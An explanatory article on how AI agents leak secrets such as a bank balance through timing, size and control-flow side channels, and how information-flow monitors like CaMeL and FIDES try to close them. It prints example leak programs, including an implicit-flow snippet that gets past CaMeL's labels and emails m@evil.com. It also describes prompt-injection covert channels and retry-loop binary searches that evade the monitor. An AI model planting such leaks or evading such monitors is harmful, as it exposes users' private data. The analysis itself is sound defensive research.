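# Side-channel leakage from AI agent systems and what unit tests can show about its mitigation

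## What is a side channel in an agent system?

A side channel is an observable by-product of a computation, such as its duration or the size of its output, from which someone can infer a secret the computation used. The classic cases come from cryptography, where the running time or power consumption of an encryption routine can reveal its key. *Rethinking Side-Channel Analysis* (2026) lists operating systems, browsers and mobile platforms among the other domains at risk, and AI agents are a recent addition.

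An agent is a language model placed in a program that lets it call tools and act on the results. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes the usual loop, which starts when the model writes a response. If the response contains a tool call, which gives the name of an outside tool and its arguments, the surrounding program runs the tool and turns the result into the next prompt. This repeats until the model writes a message for the user. Each result therefore influences what the model does next, so a secret that enters at one step can affect every later step.

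Developers can try to close such leaks, for example by padding messages to a fixed size or delaying replies. They then need to check that the change worked. The usual tool is a unit test, a short program that runs code on chosen inputs and compares the result with what the developer expected. Before writing one for a side channel, developers have to decide what counts as a leak and who could receive the leaked information.

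### The assistant and the bank balance

Suppose an assistant can read its user's bank balance, send email and fetch web pages. The balance is secret, but it can leak even if the assistant never writes it into an outgoing message.

Suppose a user tells an agent, "If I have more than 10,000 in the account, email my financial adviser and ask her to call." The email contains no figure, but an adviser who knows the rule learns from receiving it that the balance is above 10,000. If she knew an email might come, she also learns something when none does. A control-flow channel like this one leaks information through which actions the agent takes, how often, in what order, or whether they fail.

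Suppose a user asks whether they can afford a holiday. The model writes four paragraphs about hotels if their bank balance is healthy and one sentence if it is poor. Encryption hides the words but not the approximate number of bytes, so an observer can use this length channel to infer whether the balance is healthy.

In a third case, a low balance makes the assistant look up overdraft terms before it answers, so the reply takes eleven seconds instead of three. This delay is a timing channel, but side channels are hard to separate in practice, because the same web fetch delays the reply to the user, sends an unexpected request to the bank's website and produces a burst of packets that anyone on the network can see.

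### Disclosure, side channels and covert channels

These leaks differ from direct disclosure, in which the protected value itself is sent out. *Silent Egress* (2026) examines direct disclosure through an agent's tool calls. Sensitive data can leave this way while the text of the agent's answer looks clean, so the paper judges leakage by the network traffic. A filter that searches outgoing messages for the balance might catch direct disclosure, but it cannot catch "please call me", which doesn't contain the balance. *Observable Channels, Not Just Storage* (2026) covers both kinds of leak by counting any observable artifact that depends on private state, including tool-call arguments, as a possible leak. That is a sensible way to take inventory, though the two kinds need different remedies.

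The older distinction, between a side channel and a covert channel, goes back to Lampson (1973), *A Note on the Confinement Problem*. The confinement problem is how a customer can run somebody else's program on private data and be sure that the program passes nothing to its owner. Some of Lampson's leaks are crude, such as writing the data to a file that the owner can open. Others would apply to an agent today. The program can encode information in the bill for its services, since the owner must get a copy. It can also vary how much it computes and how much it reads from disk, while a second program measures the changes in the machine's speed. This second channel is noisy, but Lampson pointed out that a suitable code gets the message through as long as the effect on performance is not zero.

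Lampson used the word "covert" only for channels not intended for information transfer at all, such as the load on the machine. He classed the bill as a legitimate channel that was misused. For both, he proposed letting the customer specify all input to the channel in advance and having the operating system enforce it, if necessary by slowing the program down or making spurious disk reads. He conceded that this could be inefficient, and that a customer who can accept some leakage may prefer to limit how much information the channel carries. Most mitigations for agents are versions of one of these two ideas.

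In current use, a covert channel differs from a side channel in having a sender, a program that passes information on purpose and picks a code for it. In a side channel, an observer draws conclusions from a computation that is only doing its normal work. The path can be the same in both. *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels* describes the senders as Trojan horses, meaning untrusted programs that a malicious user has introduced, and adds that users can exploit some special kinds of covert channel without a Trojan horse.

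In an agent system, a side channel can easily become a covert channel. If the user wrote the rule about the adviser, the email is a side channel. If an attacker hid a similar rule in a web page that the assistant read, and the model obeyed it (an attack known as prompt injection), the same kind of email is a covert channel, and the attacker has chosen both the threshold and the recipient. Garby and colleagues use such a case, in which an injected line of code sends an email reading "rich!" when the balance exceeds a threshold. Researchers also use the terms loosely. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) uses "behavioral covert channels" for cases where a website offers an agent several links and infers the user's private business from the one it follows. The agent is not trying to communicate that information, so "side channel" is the better name, even though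 the website arranges the choice. The distinction matters for testing because a sender that is trying to communicate can repeat itself and correct errors, so a well-behaved agent may leak far less than a hijacked one could send through the same path.

### Who is watching

An observer is whoever tries to infer the secret, and what defines an observer is what it can see.

The network eavesdropper sits on the path between the agent and the services it uses, as an internet provider does. *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks* (Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues, 2026) represents what this observer sees as a list of triples (t, s, d), which give the time, size and direction of each packet. A real provider would normally see addresses, but the eavesdropper in this paper sees neither addresses nor content. Even so, the attack in *Whisper Leak* (2025) infers the topic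 of an encrypted conversation from packet sizes and times.

A tool server sees more detail about fewer of an agent's actions. *How Much Can Tool Calls Reveal About You?* (Duan, Liu and colleagues, 2026) studies agents that reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools. Its "local observer" is a server that receives only the calls addressed to it, including their arguments and results. Its "global observer" is a gateway or platform that every call passes through, and it can link several tasks by the same user. The attacking models correctly guessed 17.97% of the attributes in a synthetic user's profile with no trace, 26.25% with one complete task, and 32.77% with four linked tasks. A website that the agent visits is in much the same position as the local observer. In Liang and colleagues' attack, the website can log which of its pages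 the agent requests, how often, in what order and when, but it cannot see traffic to other sites.

Another customer of the same model provider is a less obvious observer. Providers often keep the processed form of a recent prompt and reuse it when a new prompt begins with the same words, so the second answer comes sooner. If customers share that store, one can guess how another's prompt begins, send the guess, and time the response to see if it matches. *Whisper Leak* lists such timing differences among the known ways to expose what someone else typed.

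Last comes the recipient of an action, like the adviser, who needs no technical access whatever.

| Observer | What it sees | What it can notice about the assistant |
|---|---|---|
| Network eavesdropper | Time, size and direction of each encrypted packet | A longer reply, a slower one, extra traffic when an email goes out |
| Tool server | Its own calls, with arguments, results and times | Whether the assistant called it, and with what |
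| Platform gateway | Every call in order, perhaps over many sessions | The balance itself, in the result of the bank call |
| Another customer | Its own response times | Whether a guessed text matches a recent prompt |
| Recipient of an action | The message, its arrival time, or its absence | That the balance is above or below the threshold |

A gateway that can read tool results has direct access to the balance, as does the bank's own tool server. It therefore makes no sense to ask whether a side channel reveals the balance to either of them.

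### Noninterference

The record of everything a given observer sees in one run is that observer's trace. Write p for the public input (here, the user's request), s for the secret, and run(p, s) for the complete execution. Let O be the function that takes an execution and returns only what the observer sees, so that O(run(p, s)) is the trace. The system has the property of noninterference for this observer if, for every public input p and all secrets s and s′,

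O(run(p, s)) = O(run(p, s′)).

The definition requires that changing only the secret never changes what the observer sees, though the trace may vary freely with p. For example, let p be the request about the adviser, and let O return the list of emails she receives. The list is empty when s = 4,000 and has one entry when s′ = 12,000, so this single pair of balances shows that the system does not meet the definition.

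The idea comes from *Security Policies and Security Models* (Goguen and Meseguer, 1982), in a slightly different form. In that paper, several users issue commands to a machine. One group of users does not interfere with another if, for every possible sequence of commands, deleting all of the first group's commands leaves the second group's output unchanged. The version for agents changes a secret value instead of deleting commands. Goguen and Meseguer assumed that the output function contains all the information the system gives its users, and they acknowledged that their model does not describe anything users learn in other ways. The version for agents makes the same assumption. If O includes packet sizes but not their times, an assistant can pass even though its delays reveal the balance.

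Language models add a complication, because they usually sample their responses at random. The same request and the same balance can produce an email today and none tomorrow, so demanding equal traces would condemn agents that leak nothing. The right demand is that the two distributions be equal: for every possible trace t,

Pr[O(run(p, s)) = t] = Pr[O(run(p, s′)) = t].

Suppose the assistant emails the adviser in 90% of runs when the balance is high and in 20% when it is low. The email is then strong evidence of a high balance, even though both outcomes are possible at either balance. Someone who compared one run at each balance would see the same outcome 26% of the time (0.9 × 0.2 plus 0.1 × 0.8) and might conclude that nothing was wrong. An assistant that ignored the balance and decided by tossing a fair coin would still show a difference in half of these comparisons.

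Garby and colleagues prove a somewhat weaker property for agents written in a small language they designed, which tracks secret values as they move through the program. The property is weaker because it allows the secret to influence whether a run finishes, which is standard in the field. They also show that the distance between the two distributions (half the sum of the absolute differences in probability) is at most the average of the two probabilities of never finishing. If 1% of runs never finish at low balances and 3% never finish at high ones, the distance is at most 2%. For agents that always finish, the weaker property is equivalent to the equality above.

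### Leakage in bits

Strict noninterference often forbids what the user asked for. An assistant that emails the adviser when the balance is high cannot satisfy it with respect to the adviser. Smith's *On the Foundations of Quantitative Information Flow* (2009) gives the example of a password checker, which has to reject wrong guesses and so always reveals something about the correct password. The next best option is to measure how much information leaks.

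An observer who can distinguish at most k outcomes learns at most log₂ k bits. This follows under Smith's measure, which is based on the chance of guessing the secret in one try. Before seeing anything, the observer's best chance is V, the probability of the most likely secret. Afterwards, it is a sum over the k outcomes, where each term is the probability that a particular secret is the true one and produces that outcome. No term can exceed V, so the sum cannot exceed kV. Observation therefore multiplies the chance of success by at most k, and the leakage in bits is the base-2 logarithm of that factor. When the program is deterministic and all secrets are equally likely, the leakage is exactly log₂ k.

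Suppose the balance is a whole number with 2²⁰ (about a million) equally likely values. The adviser's email distinguishes two outcomes, so it leaks one bit and doubles her chance of guessing the exact balance, from one in 1,048,576 to one in 524,288. If an eavesdropper can also distinguish eight reply sizes and four delay lengths, the combined trace has at most 2 × 8 × 4 = 64 outcomes and leaks at most six bits.

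Liang and colleagues tabulate the same kind of upper limit on what a website can learn by watching an agent. The presence or absence of a request can carry at most one bit, a choice among k links log₂ k bits, and the order in which the agent fetches m resources log₂ m! bits. For time and size, the limit depends on how many intervals the observer can reliably distinguish. Noise reduces the actual leakage below these limits. When the secret was one of four options, the choice of link identified it in 93.8% of the trials that produced a signal, and the timing of requests in only 58.6%.

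Smith gives two reasons why leaking only a few bits can still be unsafe. One is that an attacker can ask repeatedly. Asking whether the balance equals a particular figure leaks one bit, and so does asking whether it exceeds a figure. Twenty "equals" questions divide the million possible balances into at most 21 groups, while twenty "exceeds" questions, each chosen using the previous answers, are enough to find the exact balance. An attacker who can change the assistant's threshold once a day therefore needs at most 20 days.

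Shannon's mutual information, the more familiar measure, averages over all cases, so it can hide a rare but severe leak. Smith compares two programs that handle a 32-bit secret. The first reveals the whole secret one time in eight and otherwise almost nothing, while the second always reveals the last five bits. By mutual information, the first leaks about 4.2 bits and the second 5, so the first looks safer. But an observer's chance of guessing the secret in one try is about one in eight with the first program and one in 2²⁷ with the second. Measured by that chance, the first program leaks about 29 bits.

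### Closed to whom?

Every quantity above depends on O. Suppose a developer pads each of the assistant's replies to 8,000 bytes and holds each one until fifteen seconds have passed. If every reply fits in 8,000 bytes and is ready within fifteen seconds, the trace no longer depends on the balance for an eavesdropper who sees only the connection between user and assistant. But the assistant still emails the adviser, and it still visits the bank's website whenever the account runs low, so an eavesdropper between the assistant and the web can still see that traffic. Calling the length channel "closed" is therefore too vague unless the claim specifies the observer and the conditions. For example, a test could contradict the claim that the channel is closed to an observer who sees the size of each packet between user and assistant, for replies of up to 8,000 bytes.

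## How do loops, branches and errors leak secrets?

Some agents choose their tool calls one at a time. Others first write a short program, and an interpreter runs it and makes the calls. In both cases, a secret can affect which calls go out, how many there are and whether the run finishes. These leaks are easier to find in a written program because each one comes from a particular line of code.

### Loops

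The plainest case is a loop that runs once for every unit of the secret:

```
for i in range(balance):
    fetch("ping")
```

If the balance is 12,345, this program adds 12,345 entries to a web server's log. No request contains the balance, but whoever runs the server can learn it by counting the entries. A single run is enough, even if the balance could be any of a million values.

This loop has no honest purpose, but ordinary tasks can have the same structure. Suppose the user asks the assistant to fetch the payment page for each unpaid bill, and one billing company hosts all the pages. The company may already know about the bills, but an eavesdropper who counts the bursts of traffic can make a good estimate of how many are unpaid.

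The request count is exact when an interpreter runs the loop, and less reliable when a model makes the calls one by one. Among the trials that produced a signal in the four-option test by Liang and colleagues, the website identified the secret 73.5% of the time by counting requests and 89.6% of the time by checking only whether a request arrived. The researchers name caching and the removal of duplicate requests as the main sources of counting errors.

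Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, use a loop like the one above as an example and propose several remedies. In CaMeL, an agent design by Debenedetti and colleagues, one model writes a program from the user's request, a second model that cannot call tools reads untrusted text, and an interpreter checks each tool call against a security policy. Tallam and Miller, who work for the company SentinelAI, mention internal tests of some of their other ideas but report no experiments on the side-channel remedies. Their bibliography entry for CaMeL wrongly gives the title of *Poisoning Language Models During Instruction Tuning* (2023) and links to a third paper, *Not what you've signed up for* (2023), which is about prompt injection. Anyone relying on their account of CaMeL should check it against the original.

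One proposed mitigation is to cap the number of iterations when it depends on a secret. With a cap of c, the server can still receive anywhere from 0 to c requests, so c + 1 outcomes remain possible. An attacker who can influence the program can use all of these outcomes by rescaling the secret. With a cap of nine, a loop over `range(balance // 100000)` reveals the first digit of a six-digit balance. The next run can reveal the second digit, and six runs reveal the whole number. Since r runs can distinguish (c + 1)ʳ values, finding one of 1,000,000 possible balances takes the smallest r for which (c + 1)ʳ is at least 1,000,000.

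| Cap on iterations | Outcomes per run | Bits per run, at most | Runs to find one value in 1,000,000 |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 1 |
| 999 | 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 |
| 99 | 100 | 6.6 | 3 |
| 9 | 10 | 3.3 | 6 |
| 1 | 2 | 1.0 | 20 |

Even the tightest cap that still allows the loop to run slows the attacker by only a factor of twenty. It also breaks legitimate tasks, since an assistant with a cap of nine never gets to the tenth unpaid bill.

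Tallam and Miller mention rejecting the loop as an alternative to cutting it short. If the interpreter rejects only the loops that would exceed the cap, a rejection reveals that the secret is large. To stop the count from leaking, the interpreter has to reject every loop whose length depends on a secret, including the short ones.

They also suggest combining repeated calls into a single bulk request. The agent then always sends one request, but the request's size can still reveal the number of items. If it lists 12,345 pings, the server can count them, and an eavesdropper can estimate the number from the length of the encrypted message. To stop the eavesdropper, the agent has to pad every batch to the same length and send one even when there is nothing to fetch, because a missing request would reveal that there were no items. Hiding the number from the server is harder, because the server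 can ignore any padding it recognises. The agent would have to fill the batch with items that look real, for example by requesting the pages of all the year's bills, paid and unpaid.

### Branches

A branch that sends an email only if the balance exceeds a threshold leaks at most one bit per run. Repeated runs can leak more, depending on who sets the threshold. In the earlier example, the user set it at 10,000, so the adviser learns nothing new if the assistant repeats the task while the balance stays the same.

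An attacker who can change the threshold before each run can do much better. Suppose the balance is a whole number from 0 to 999,999. The best strategy is binary search, in which each threshold splits the remaining values in half. The attacker starts with 499,999. If no email arrives, the balance is at most 499,999, and the next threshold is 249,999. If the true balance is 12,345, the first six runs produce no email, which tells the attacker that the balance is below 15,625. The seventh threshold, 7,812, produces the first email. Ten runs narrow the balance to a range of at most 1,000 values, and twenty identify it exactly.

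Errors make the search longer but don't stop it. In Liang and colleagues' test of presence or absence, the website got 6.2% of the bits wrong. If a binary search had the same error rate and the errors were independent, all twenty answers would be right only 28% of the time. Asking each question three times and taking the majority answer raises this to 80%, and asking five times raises it to 96% but takes 100 runs.

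Limiting the number of runs therefore limits how much an attacker can learn. With five runs, an attacker can at best narrow a million values to about 31,250. The search can also reach the wrong answer if the balance changes partway through, such as when a salary is paid. But a developer can't rely on a run limit or a changing balance if the agent repeats its own work. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's automatic retries can cause this repetition, and that an attacker can rewrite the branch so that the interpreter fails to block it.

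One way to close the channel is to forbid the branch. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) considered a rule that would do this. Once an agent had called a tool that might read a secret, it could no longer call any tool whose effects an outsider might observe. They judged this too restrictive for practical use. Under such a rule, the assistant could not email anyone after looking at the balance. Their own design, FIDES, stops the agent from copying secrets into places where they don't belong, but they acknowledge that an observer of the sequence of tool calls can still infer limited information from the agent's decisions.

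FIDES can also limit how much information an answer can carry. An isolated model reads the private text and returns only yes or no, or one item from a short list. A policy can then allow that answer in places where it forbids free text. But the limit applies to each answer separately, so twenty well-chosen yes-or-no answers are enough for the binary search above.

### Errors

An error can leak a secret when it occurs for some values and not for others. Consider a program that moves money and then reports to the adviser:

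```
transfer(5000, to="savings")
send_email(adviser, "The transfer is done.")
```

If the account holds less than 5,000, the bank's tool raises an exception, which stops the program unless other code handles it. The program never reaches the second line, so an adviser expecting the email can infer that the balance is too low.

It is tempting to conclude that errors leak at most one bit per run, since a run either finishes or doesn't. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit* (2008), showed that this is wrong if the program produces output before it stops. Their example counts upwards, publishes each number, and goes into an endless loop when it reaches the secret. The last number published is the secret. A crash works just as well as an endless loop, so an agent's version could look like this:

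```
for i in range(1000000):
    fetch("ping")
    if i == balance:
        crash()
```

The server receives one more request than the balance, and then the requests stop. The loop's bound is always 1,000,000, so a rule that applies only to loops with a secret bound, like one of Tallam and Miller's proposals, would not catch this leak. The established tools for checking information flow in source code didn't catch it either. Askarov and colleagues wrote versions of their example for Jif, FlowCaml and SPARK, whose analyses accept such programs as secure.

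The method is slow because the program has to count up to the secret value. In their fastest test, it leaked a 32-bit number in under six seconds on a 3 GHz processor. From this they estimated that a credit card number would take about eighteen and a half days, and they considered leaking a 128-bit encryption key infeasible. An agent would be slower, since at ten web requests a second it would need about 28 hours to count to a million.

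Askarov and colleagues also proved that such a program can leak no more in a single run than it would by counting, provided that the secret affects only whether the program keeps going and never what it publishes. A program that produces at most t outputs then has at most t + 1 possible outcomes, the same as a loop capped at t. If the secret is a random number of N bits, watching the run improves an observer's chance of guessing it by at most t/2ᴺ. This bound is reassuring for an encryption key, where 2ᴺ is enormous, but much less so for a bank balance, which has only about a million plausible values and which an attacker may be able to probe more than once.

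Tallam and Miller propose replacing exceptions with explicit result values. Instead of stopping the program, a failed transfer returns a value that marks it as failed, and the program carries on. But if the next line emails the adviser only when the transfer succeeded, she can still infer the outcome from whether she gets an email. To close this leak, what she sees must be the same in both cases. For example, the program could always email her "I have dealt with the transfer request" and show the outcome only to the user. Tallam and Miller recognise this and ask for both paths to have the same structure and timing.

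In Garby and colleagues' programming language, a program that asks a model for a value gets back either "true" with the value or "false" with an error message. One of their sample programs responds to an error by returning the message to the model and asking again, up to five times. Success on the first attempt takes one request and failure takes several, so the two paths differ even though the result is explicit. If a secret affected whether the model's first response was valid, anyone who could count the requests would learn something about the secret.

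### Making every run look the same

A more thorough remedy is to have the agent follow a fixed schedule, making the same calls in the same order on every run, whether or not it needs them. Lampson's spurious disk reads were an early version of this. The assistant would look up the overdraft terms every time someone asked about a holiday, and discard them if the balance was healthy. An observer who sees only which calls occur would then learn nothing about the balance, though one who also sees their arguments or sizes may still learn something unless those are the same on every run too.

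The schedule has to be long enough for the worst case. If a user can have up to 40 unpaid bills, the assistant has to make 40 requests on every run, even if the user usually has two. If the tool charges per call, a typical run then costs twenty times as much.

Dummy calls can also do harm. An unnecessary request for a public web page is usually harmless, though it may use up a quota. An unnecessary payment does harm, and so does an email that prompts an adviser to phone the user for no reason. Sending the dummy email to another address would fool an eavesdropper but not the adviser, who would still receive nothing.

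Random dummy calls add less overhead than a fixed schedule but give much weaker protection. Suppose the assistant always fetches the overdraft terms when the balance is low, and also fetches them in 30% of runs when the balance is healthy. If the two cases were equally likely beforehand, an observer who sees the request can put the chance of a low balance at 77%, and one who doesn't see it knows that the balance is healthy. Repeated runs reveal more. A healthy account would produce the request in all ten of ten runs only about six times in a million, so ten requests in a row leave very little doubt that the balance is low.

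Liang and colleagues measured the overhead of a remedy of this general kind. Their system fetches everything a web page links to, regardless of the user's task, and the agent then picks what it needs from the local copies. If the agent needs something that isn't there, the system mixes the new request with others chosen independently of the task. On 500 questions from the Stack Exchange websites, the average number of page fetches per question rose from 6.5 to 27.9, and the time from 224 to 285 seconds.

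The remedy reduced the leak but did not stop it. The attacker recovered 92% of the concepts in a user's question without the remedy and 91% with it. But the attacker also made more wrong guesses with the remedy in place, so the share of guesses that were correct fell from 87% to 29%. An attack designed to filter out the remedy's extra requests might do better than these figures suggest.

### Asking the user

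The remaining option is to let the user decide. Tallam and Miller want CaMeL's interpreter to switch to STRICT mode automatically for any loop whose bound is secret. Calls that change something would then fail or wait for the user's confirmation.

Confirmation doesn't reduce the leak if the user says yes. The email to the adviser still goes out and reveals that the balance is above 10,000. The user's agreement has some value if the question explains what the adviser will be able to infer, but "Send this email?" doesn't explain that. Tallam and Miller also point out that users who see many such questions tend to approve them without reading, and would therefore reserve the strictest checks for irreversible or externally visible actions such as sending email.

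Asking the user can also leak information. If the assistant asks only when the balance is high, an eavesdropper on the user's connection may notice the extra message or the pause while the user decides. For email, Tallam and Miller propose approval by more than one method. If one method is a text message, the phone company can also observe the request. To avoid these leaks, the assistant would have to ask before it reads the balance, or ask every time.

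Blocking and asking also get in the way of ordinary work. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with GPT-5.2 on the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a standard test of agents under prompt injection. Without attacks, CaMeL completed 32 of 48 runs with its policy checks off and 18 with them on. With MiMo-v2.5, turning the checks on reduced the number from 34 to 18. The estimates are rough because the 48 runs were three attempts at each of 16 tasks, and Garby and colleagues have a competing design. The checks also cover direct disclosure and untrusted data, so the drop shows the effect of the whole policy, not of closing any one control-flow channel.

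## Can information-flow tracking close control-flow leaks?

Forbidding a branch on a secret, or asking the user about it, works only if the software running the agent can detect that the branch depends on one. Information-flow tracking is one way to detect this: it attaches a label such as "secret" to each value, carries the label through the computation, and checks it wherever a value could leave the system.

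### How labels spread

The simplest scheme has two labels, public and secret. A value computed from other values takes the most restrictive of their labels. If the balance is secret, `balance / 2` is secret too, and so is any text that contains either. Before an email is sent, a policy check compares the label on its text with what the recipient may read.

Richer schemes list the permitted readers. In an example from Costa and colleagues, users A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D another, so only B and C may read anything made from both. Many systems also keep an integrity label, which records whether a value comes from a trusted source and helps against prompt injection. For leaks, the labels that matter are confidentiality labels, such as these lists of readers.

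Tracking is coarser with a language model because it is hard to tell which parts of a prompt influenced the response. FIDES therefore gives the response the combined label of everything in the prompt. Once the balance is in the prompt of the assistant's model, even a response of "Good morning" is labelled secret.

These rules follow data that the program copies or computes with. In a written program, they miss an email whose text is a fixed phrase:

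```
if balance > 10000:
    contacted = True
    send_email(adviser, "Please call me.")
```

Neither `True` nor "Please call me." comes from the balance, so to catch this leak the tracker also needs a label for the program's current position, called the program-counter label. It starts as public, becomes secret when the program enters a branch with a secret condition, and returns to its earlier value when the branch ends. Everything the program does inside the branch takes on that label. Here `contacted` becomes secret, and the policy check treats the email as if it contained a secret. The same rule covers loops, so the tracker can stop `for i in range(balance): fetch("ping")` at the first ping. Garby and colleagues trace the idea to a 1977 paper by Denning and Denning.

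### CaMeL and STRICT mode

In CaMeL, a planning model writes the program, and a separate, quarantined model reads untrusted text. As the interpreter runs the program, it labels each value with where it came from and who may read it, and uses those labels in its policy checks.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) explains how this separation protects a single agent and shows that it can fail when agents call one another. With a single agent, untrusted data can influence which of the program's branches runs, but it cannot add a new branch. If the program for a holiday question contains no call to the email tool, no web page can make it send an email.

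That guarantee concerns who controls the program, so a branch already in the program can still reveal the balance. A program-counter label is meant to prevent this leak, and CaMeL has one. Garby and colleagues confirm that CaMeL's interpreter blocks an email sent directly inside a branch that depends on the balance.

The interpreter would also need labels to decide when to switch to STRICT mode, which Tallam and Miller propose for loops with a secret bound. A loop whose secret bound was wrongly labelled public would never trigger it. Even with correct labels, the mode might not stop the page fetches in their own example, because it restricts only calls that change something. Fetching a page usually changes nothing, but the server can still count the fetches. The mode would have to cover every call that an outsider can observe.

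### The branch not taken

CaMeL's interpreter assigns labels as it runs the program, so it changes a variable's label only when it executes an assignment to that variable. Garby and colleagues found that this lets a secret slip through. With a threshold of 10,000, their leak can take this form:

```
1  rich = True
2  tmp = True
3  if balance > 10000: tmp = False
4  if tmp: rich = False
5  if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
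```

| Line | Balance of 12,000 | Balance of 4,000 |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `rich` is True and public | `rich` is True and public |
| 2 | `tmp` is True and public | `tmp` is True and public |
| 3 | The assignment runs: `tmp` becomes False and secret | The interpreter skips the assignment: `tmp` stays True and public |
| 4 | The interpreter skips the assignment: `rich` stays True and public | The assignment runs: `rich` becomes False and stays public |
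| 5 | The condition is public, so the email goes out | The condition is false, so there is no email |

With a balance of 12,000, the interpreter correctly labels `tmp` secret at line 3, because the assignment happens under a secret program-counter label. Tracking fails at line 4. Whether `rich` changes there depends on `tmp`, and therefore on the balance, but the interpreter skips the assignment and leaves `rich` with its label from line 1. With a balance of 4,000, tracking fails at line 3. The interpreter skips the assignment to `tmp`, leaves its label public, and then treats line 4 as a branch on public data.

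In both runs `rich` ends up public, and its value reveals whether the balance is above 10,000. Garby and colleagues credit the original example to Fenton (1974) and the version in ordinary program code to Denning (1976). Other researchers rediscovered it decades later.

A program can leak more than one bit by repeating these lines with a new threshold each time. The earlier answers are in public variables, so the program can use them to choose the next threshold. Twenty rounds in a single run are enough to recover any balance below a million. The recovered number is labelled public, so the program can then email it.

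An attacker still has to get CaMeL's planning model to write such a program. That model never receives untrusted tool results, but CaMeL treats the user's request as trusted. Tallam and Miller point out that an attacker can use phishing or a chat conversation to get a crafted prompt into that request.

### The classic repairs

One repair is to analyse the whole program before running it. If a branch depends on a secret, the analysis marks as secret every variable that the branch could change, even if a particular run doesn't take the branch. In the example, it marks `tmp` as secret after line 3 and `rich` after line 4, for either balance. Line 5 therefore branches on a secret, and the analysis can reject the program.

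This analysis also rejects some harmless programs. For example, it marks a variable as secret even if both sides of the branch give it the same value. It also needs the complete code in advance. CaMeL's planning model writes its program before it runs, but in Python, which is hard to analyze because its types are flexible, it has exceptions, and its programs can inspect and modify themselves. Tallam and Miller therefore suggest a smaller language with bounded loops and labels built into its types. Advance analysis is even harder for an agent that generates more code as it runs.

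The other repair keeps the tracking at run time but stops the program before it can change a public variable under a secret program-counter label. Austin and Flanagan introduced this rule in 2009, and Garby and colleagues call it "no-high-upgrade". With a balance of 12,000, the program stops at line 3, and with 4,000 it runs to the end without sending anything, so the attacker receives no email in either case.

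This rule can stop useful programs too. In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, a program sends a message to a model inside a branch that depends on a secret, but the conversation so far is public. Adding the message would make the conversation secret only in runs that take the branch, so the interpreter stops the program. A developer can avoid this by marking the conversation as secret beforehand, but then everything the model writes in it is secret too.

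Stopping the program also leaks information. In the email example, the program stops when the balance is high and finishes when it is low, so anyone who can tell whether it finished learns which it is.

### The retry loop outside the monitor

A program that produces no output before it stops can leak at most one bit per run through whether it finishes. Garby and colleagues' second leak in CaMeL uses repeated runs to leak more than one bit in total.

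When a CaMeL program fails, ordinary Python code outside the interpreter calls the planning model again to get a new program. The interpreter does not track this retry loop, so each new program starts with clean labels, even though the planning model may have written it in response to an error that depended on a secret.

Suppose the first program tries to send an email only if the balance exceeds 499,999. The interpreter blocks the email if the program tries to send it, so whether the interpreter intervenes reveals one bit about the balance. If whoever steers the attempts can use that outcome to set the next threshold, the binary search described earlier recovers the whole balance. A later program could then contain the balance as an ordinary number, which has no secret label because it came from the planning model.

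CaMeL censors the error messages it passes back, which limits how much each failure reveals, but according to Garby and colleagues this comes with no formal guarantee. Censoring also cannot hide that an attempt failed, because the failure triggers the next attempt. Capping the loop at r attempts would limit the leak to r bits if each attempt revealed only whether the interpreter blocked it.

The same problem can arise outside the interpreter. A scheduler that restarts a failed agent, or a user who rewords a request after an error, also creates a loop that the interpreter does not track.

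### What FIDES leaves untracked

FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. Explicit secrecy applies to each path through a program, meaning a fixed sequence of actions. If two data stores have matching public data before the same path runs on each, their public data must still match afterwards. The property doesn't restrict which path the program takes.

The program that emails the adviser "Please call me." has two paths, one that sends the fixed text and one that does nothing. Each path has the same public effect whatever the balance is, so the program satisfies explicit secrecy. The ping loop does too, because 12,345 pings and 12,346 pings are different paths. Costa and colleagues call this kind of leak limited, but the definition doesn't limit how much a program can leak this way.

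They find noninterference too restrictive, and they cite web browsers and TaintDroid, a system that tracks private data on Android phones, as precedents for the same compromise.

FIDES can be stricter than explicit secrecy requires. If its planning model has read the balance, every later tool call it writes carries the secret label, and a policy can block an email to anyone not allowed to know the balance. To avoid this, FIDES can keep the balance in a variable and show the planning model only the variable's name. The isolated model described earlier can then answer a question about the balance, such as whether it exceeds 10,000.

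FIDES adds the answer's type to its label, so a policy can treat a secret yes or no more leniently than secret text. Costa and colleagues argue that such a small answer is poorly suited to carrying an injected instruction or stolen data. Such a policy can let the adviser's email go out, and the email reveals the answer.

Garby and colleagues object that these exceptions are hard to audit. When a yes-or-no value passes the check, no one can tell from the record of the run whether it was the exception the developer intended or a leak of the same form. Costa and colleagues' tests do not resolve this objection, because they left out the mechanism that forces answers into a fixed type. In those tests, Costa and colleagues also hid values from the planning model based only on integrity labels, and relied on policies to protect confidentiality.

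The tests show why developers want exceptions. With GPT-4o on AgentDojo's banking tasks, policy checks cut a basic agent's success rate from 98.8% to 37.5%. They cut FIDES's rate from 65.0% to 52.5%, so FIDES outperformed the basic agent only when the checks were on.

### What the LLMbda theorems guarantee

LLMbda, a small language that Garby and colleagues designed, tracks branches on secrets. It labels every value and the conversation with the model. If the model writes code after reading a secret, that code runs with a secret program-counter label from its first line. The no-high-upgrade rule prevents leaks through the branch that isn't taken.

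Their main theorem covers every program in the language, including agents that generate and run code. The property is called termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. For a secret s, let μₛ(t) be the probability that a run finishes and the observer sees the result t. These probabilities can add up to less than 1, and the remainder is the probability that the run never finishes. The theorem says that for any two secrets s and s′,

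Σₜ max(μₛ(t), μₛ′(t)) ≤ 1.

For example, suppose that at a low balance 60% of runs finish with an email, 30% finish without one and 10% never finish. At a high balance, the figures are 50%, 40% and 10%. The larger value is 60% for finishing with an email and 40% for finishing without one. These add up to 100%, so the property holds. The property allows this difference because the unfinished runs could account for all of it. If those at the low balance had finished without an email and those at the high balance with one, both balances would show 60% and 40%. But if every run finishes, a split of 60% and 40% at one balance and 50% and 50% at the other violates the property, because the larger values add up to 110%.

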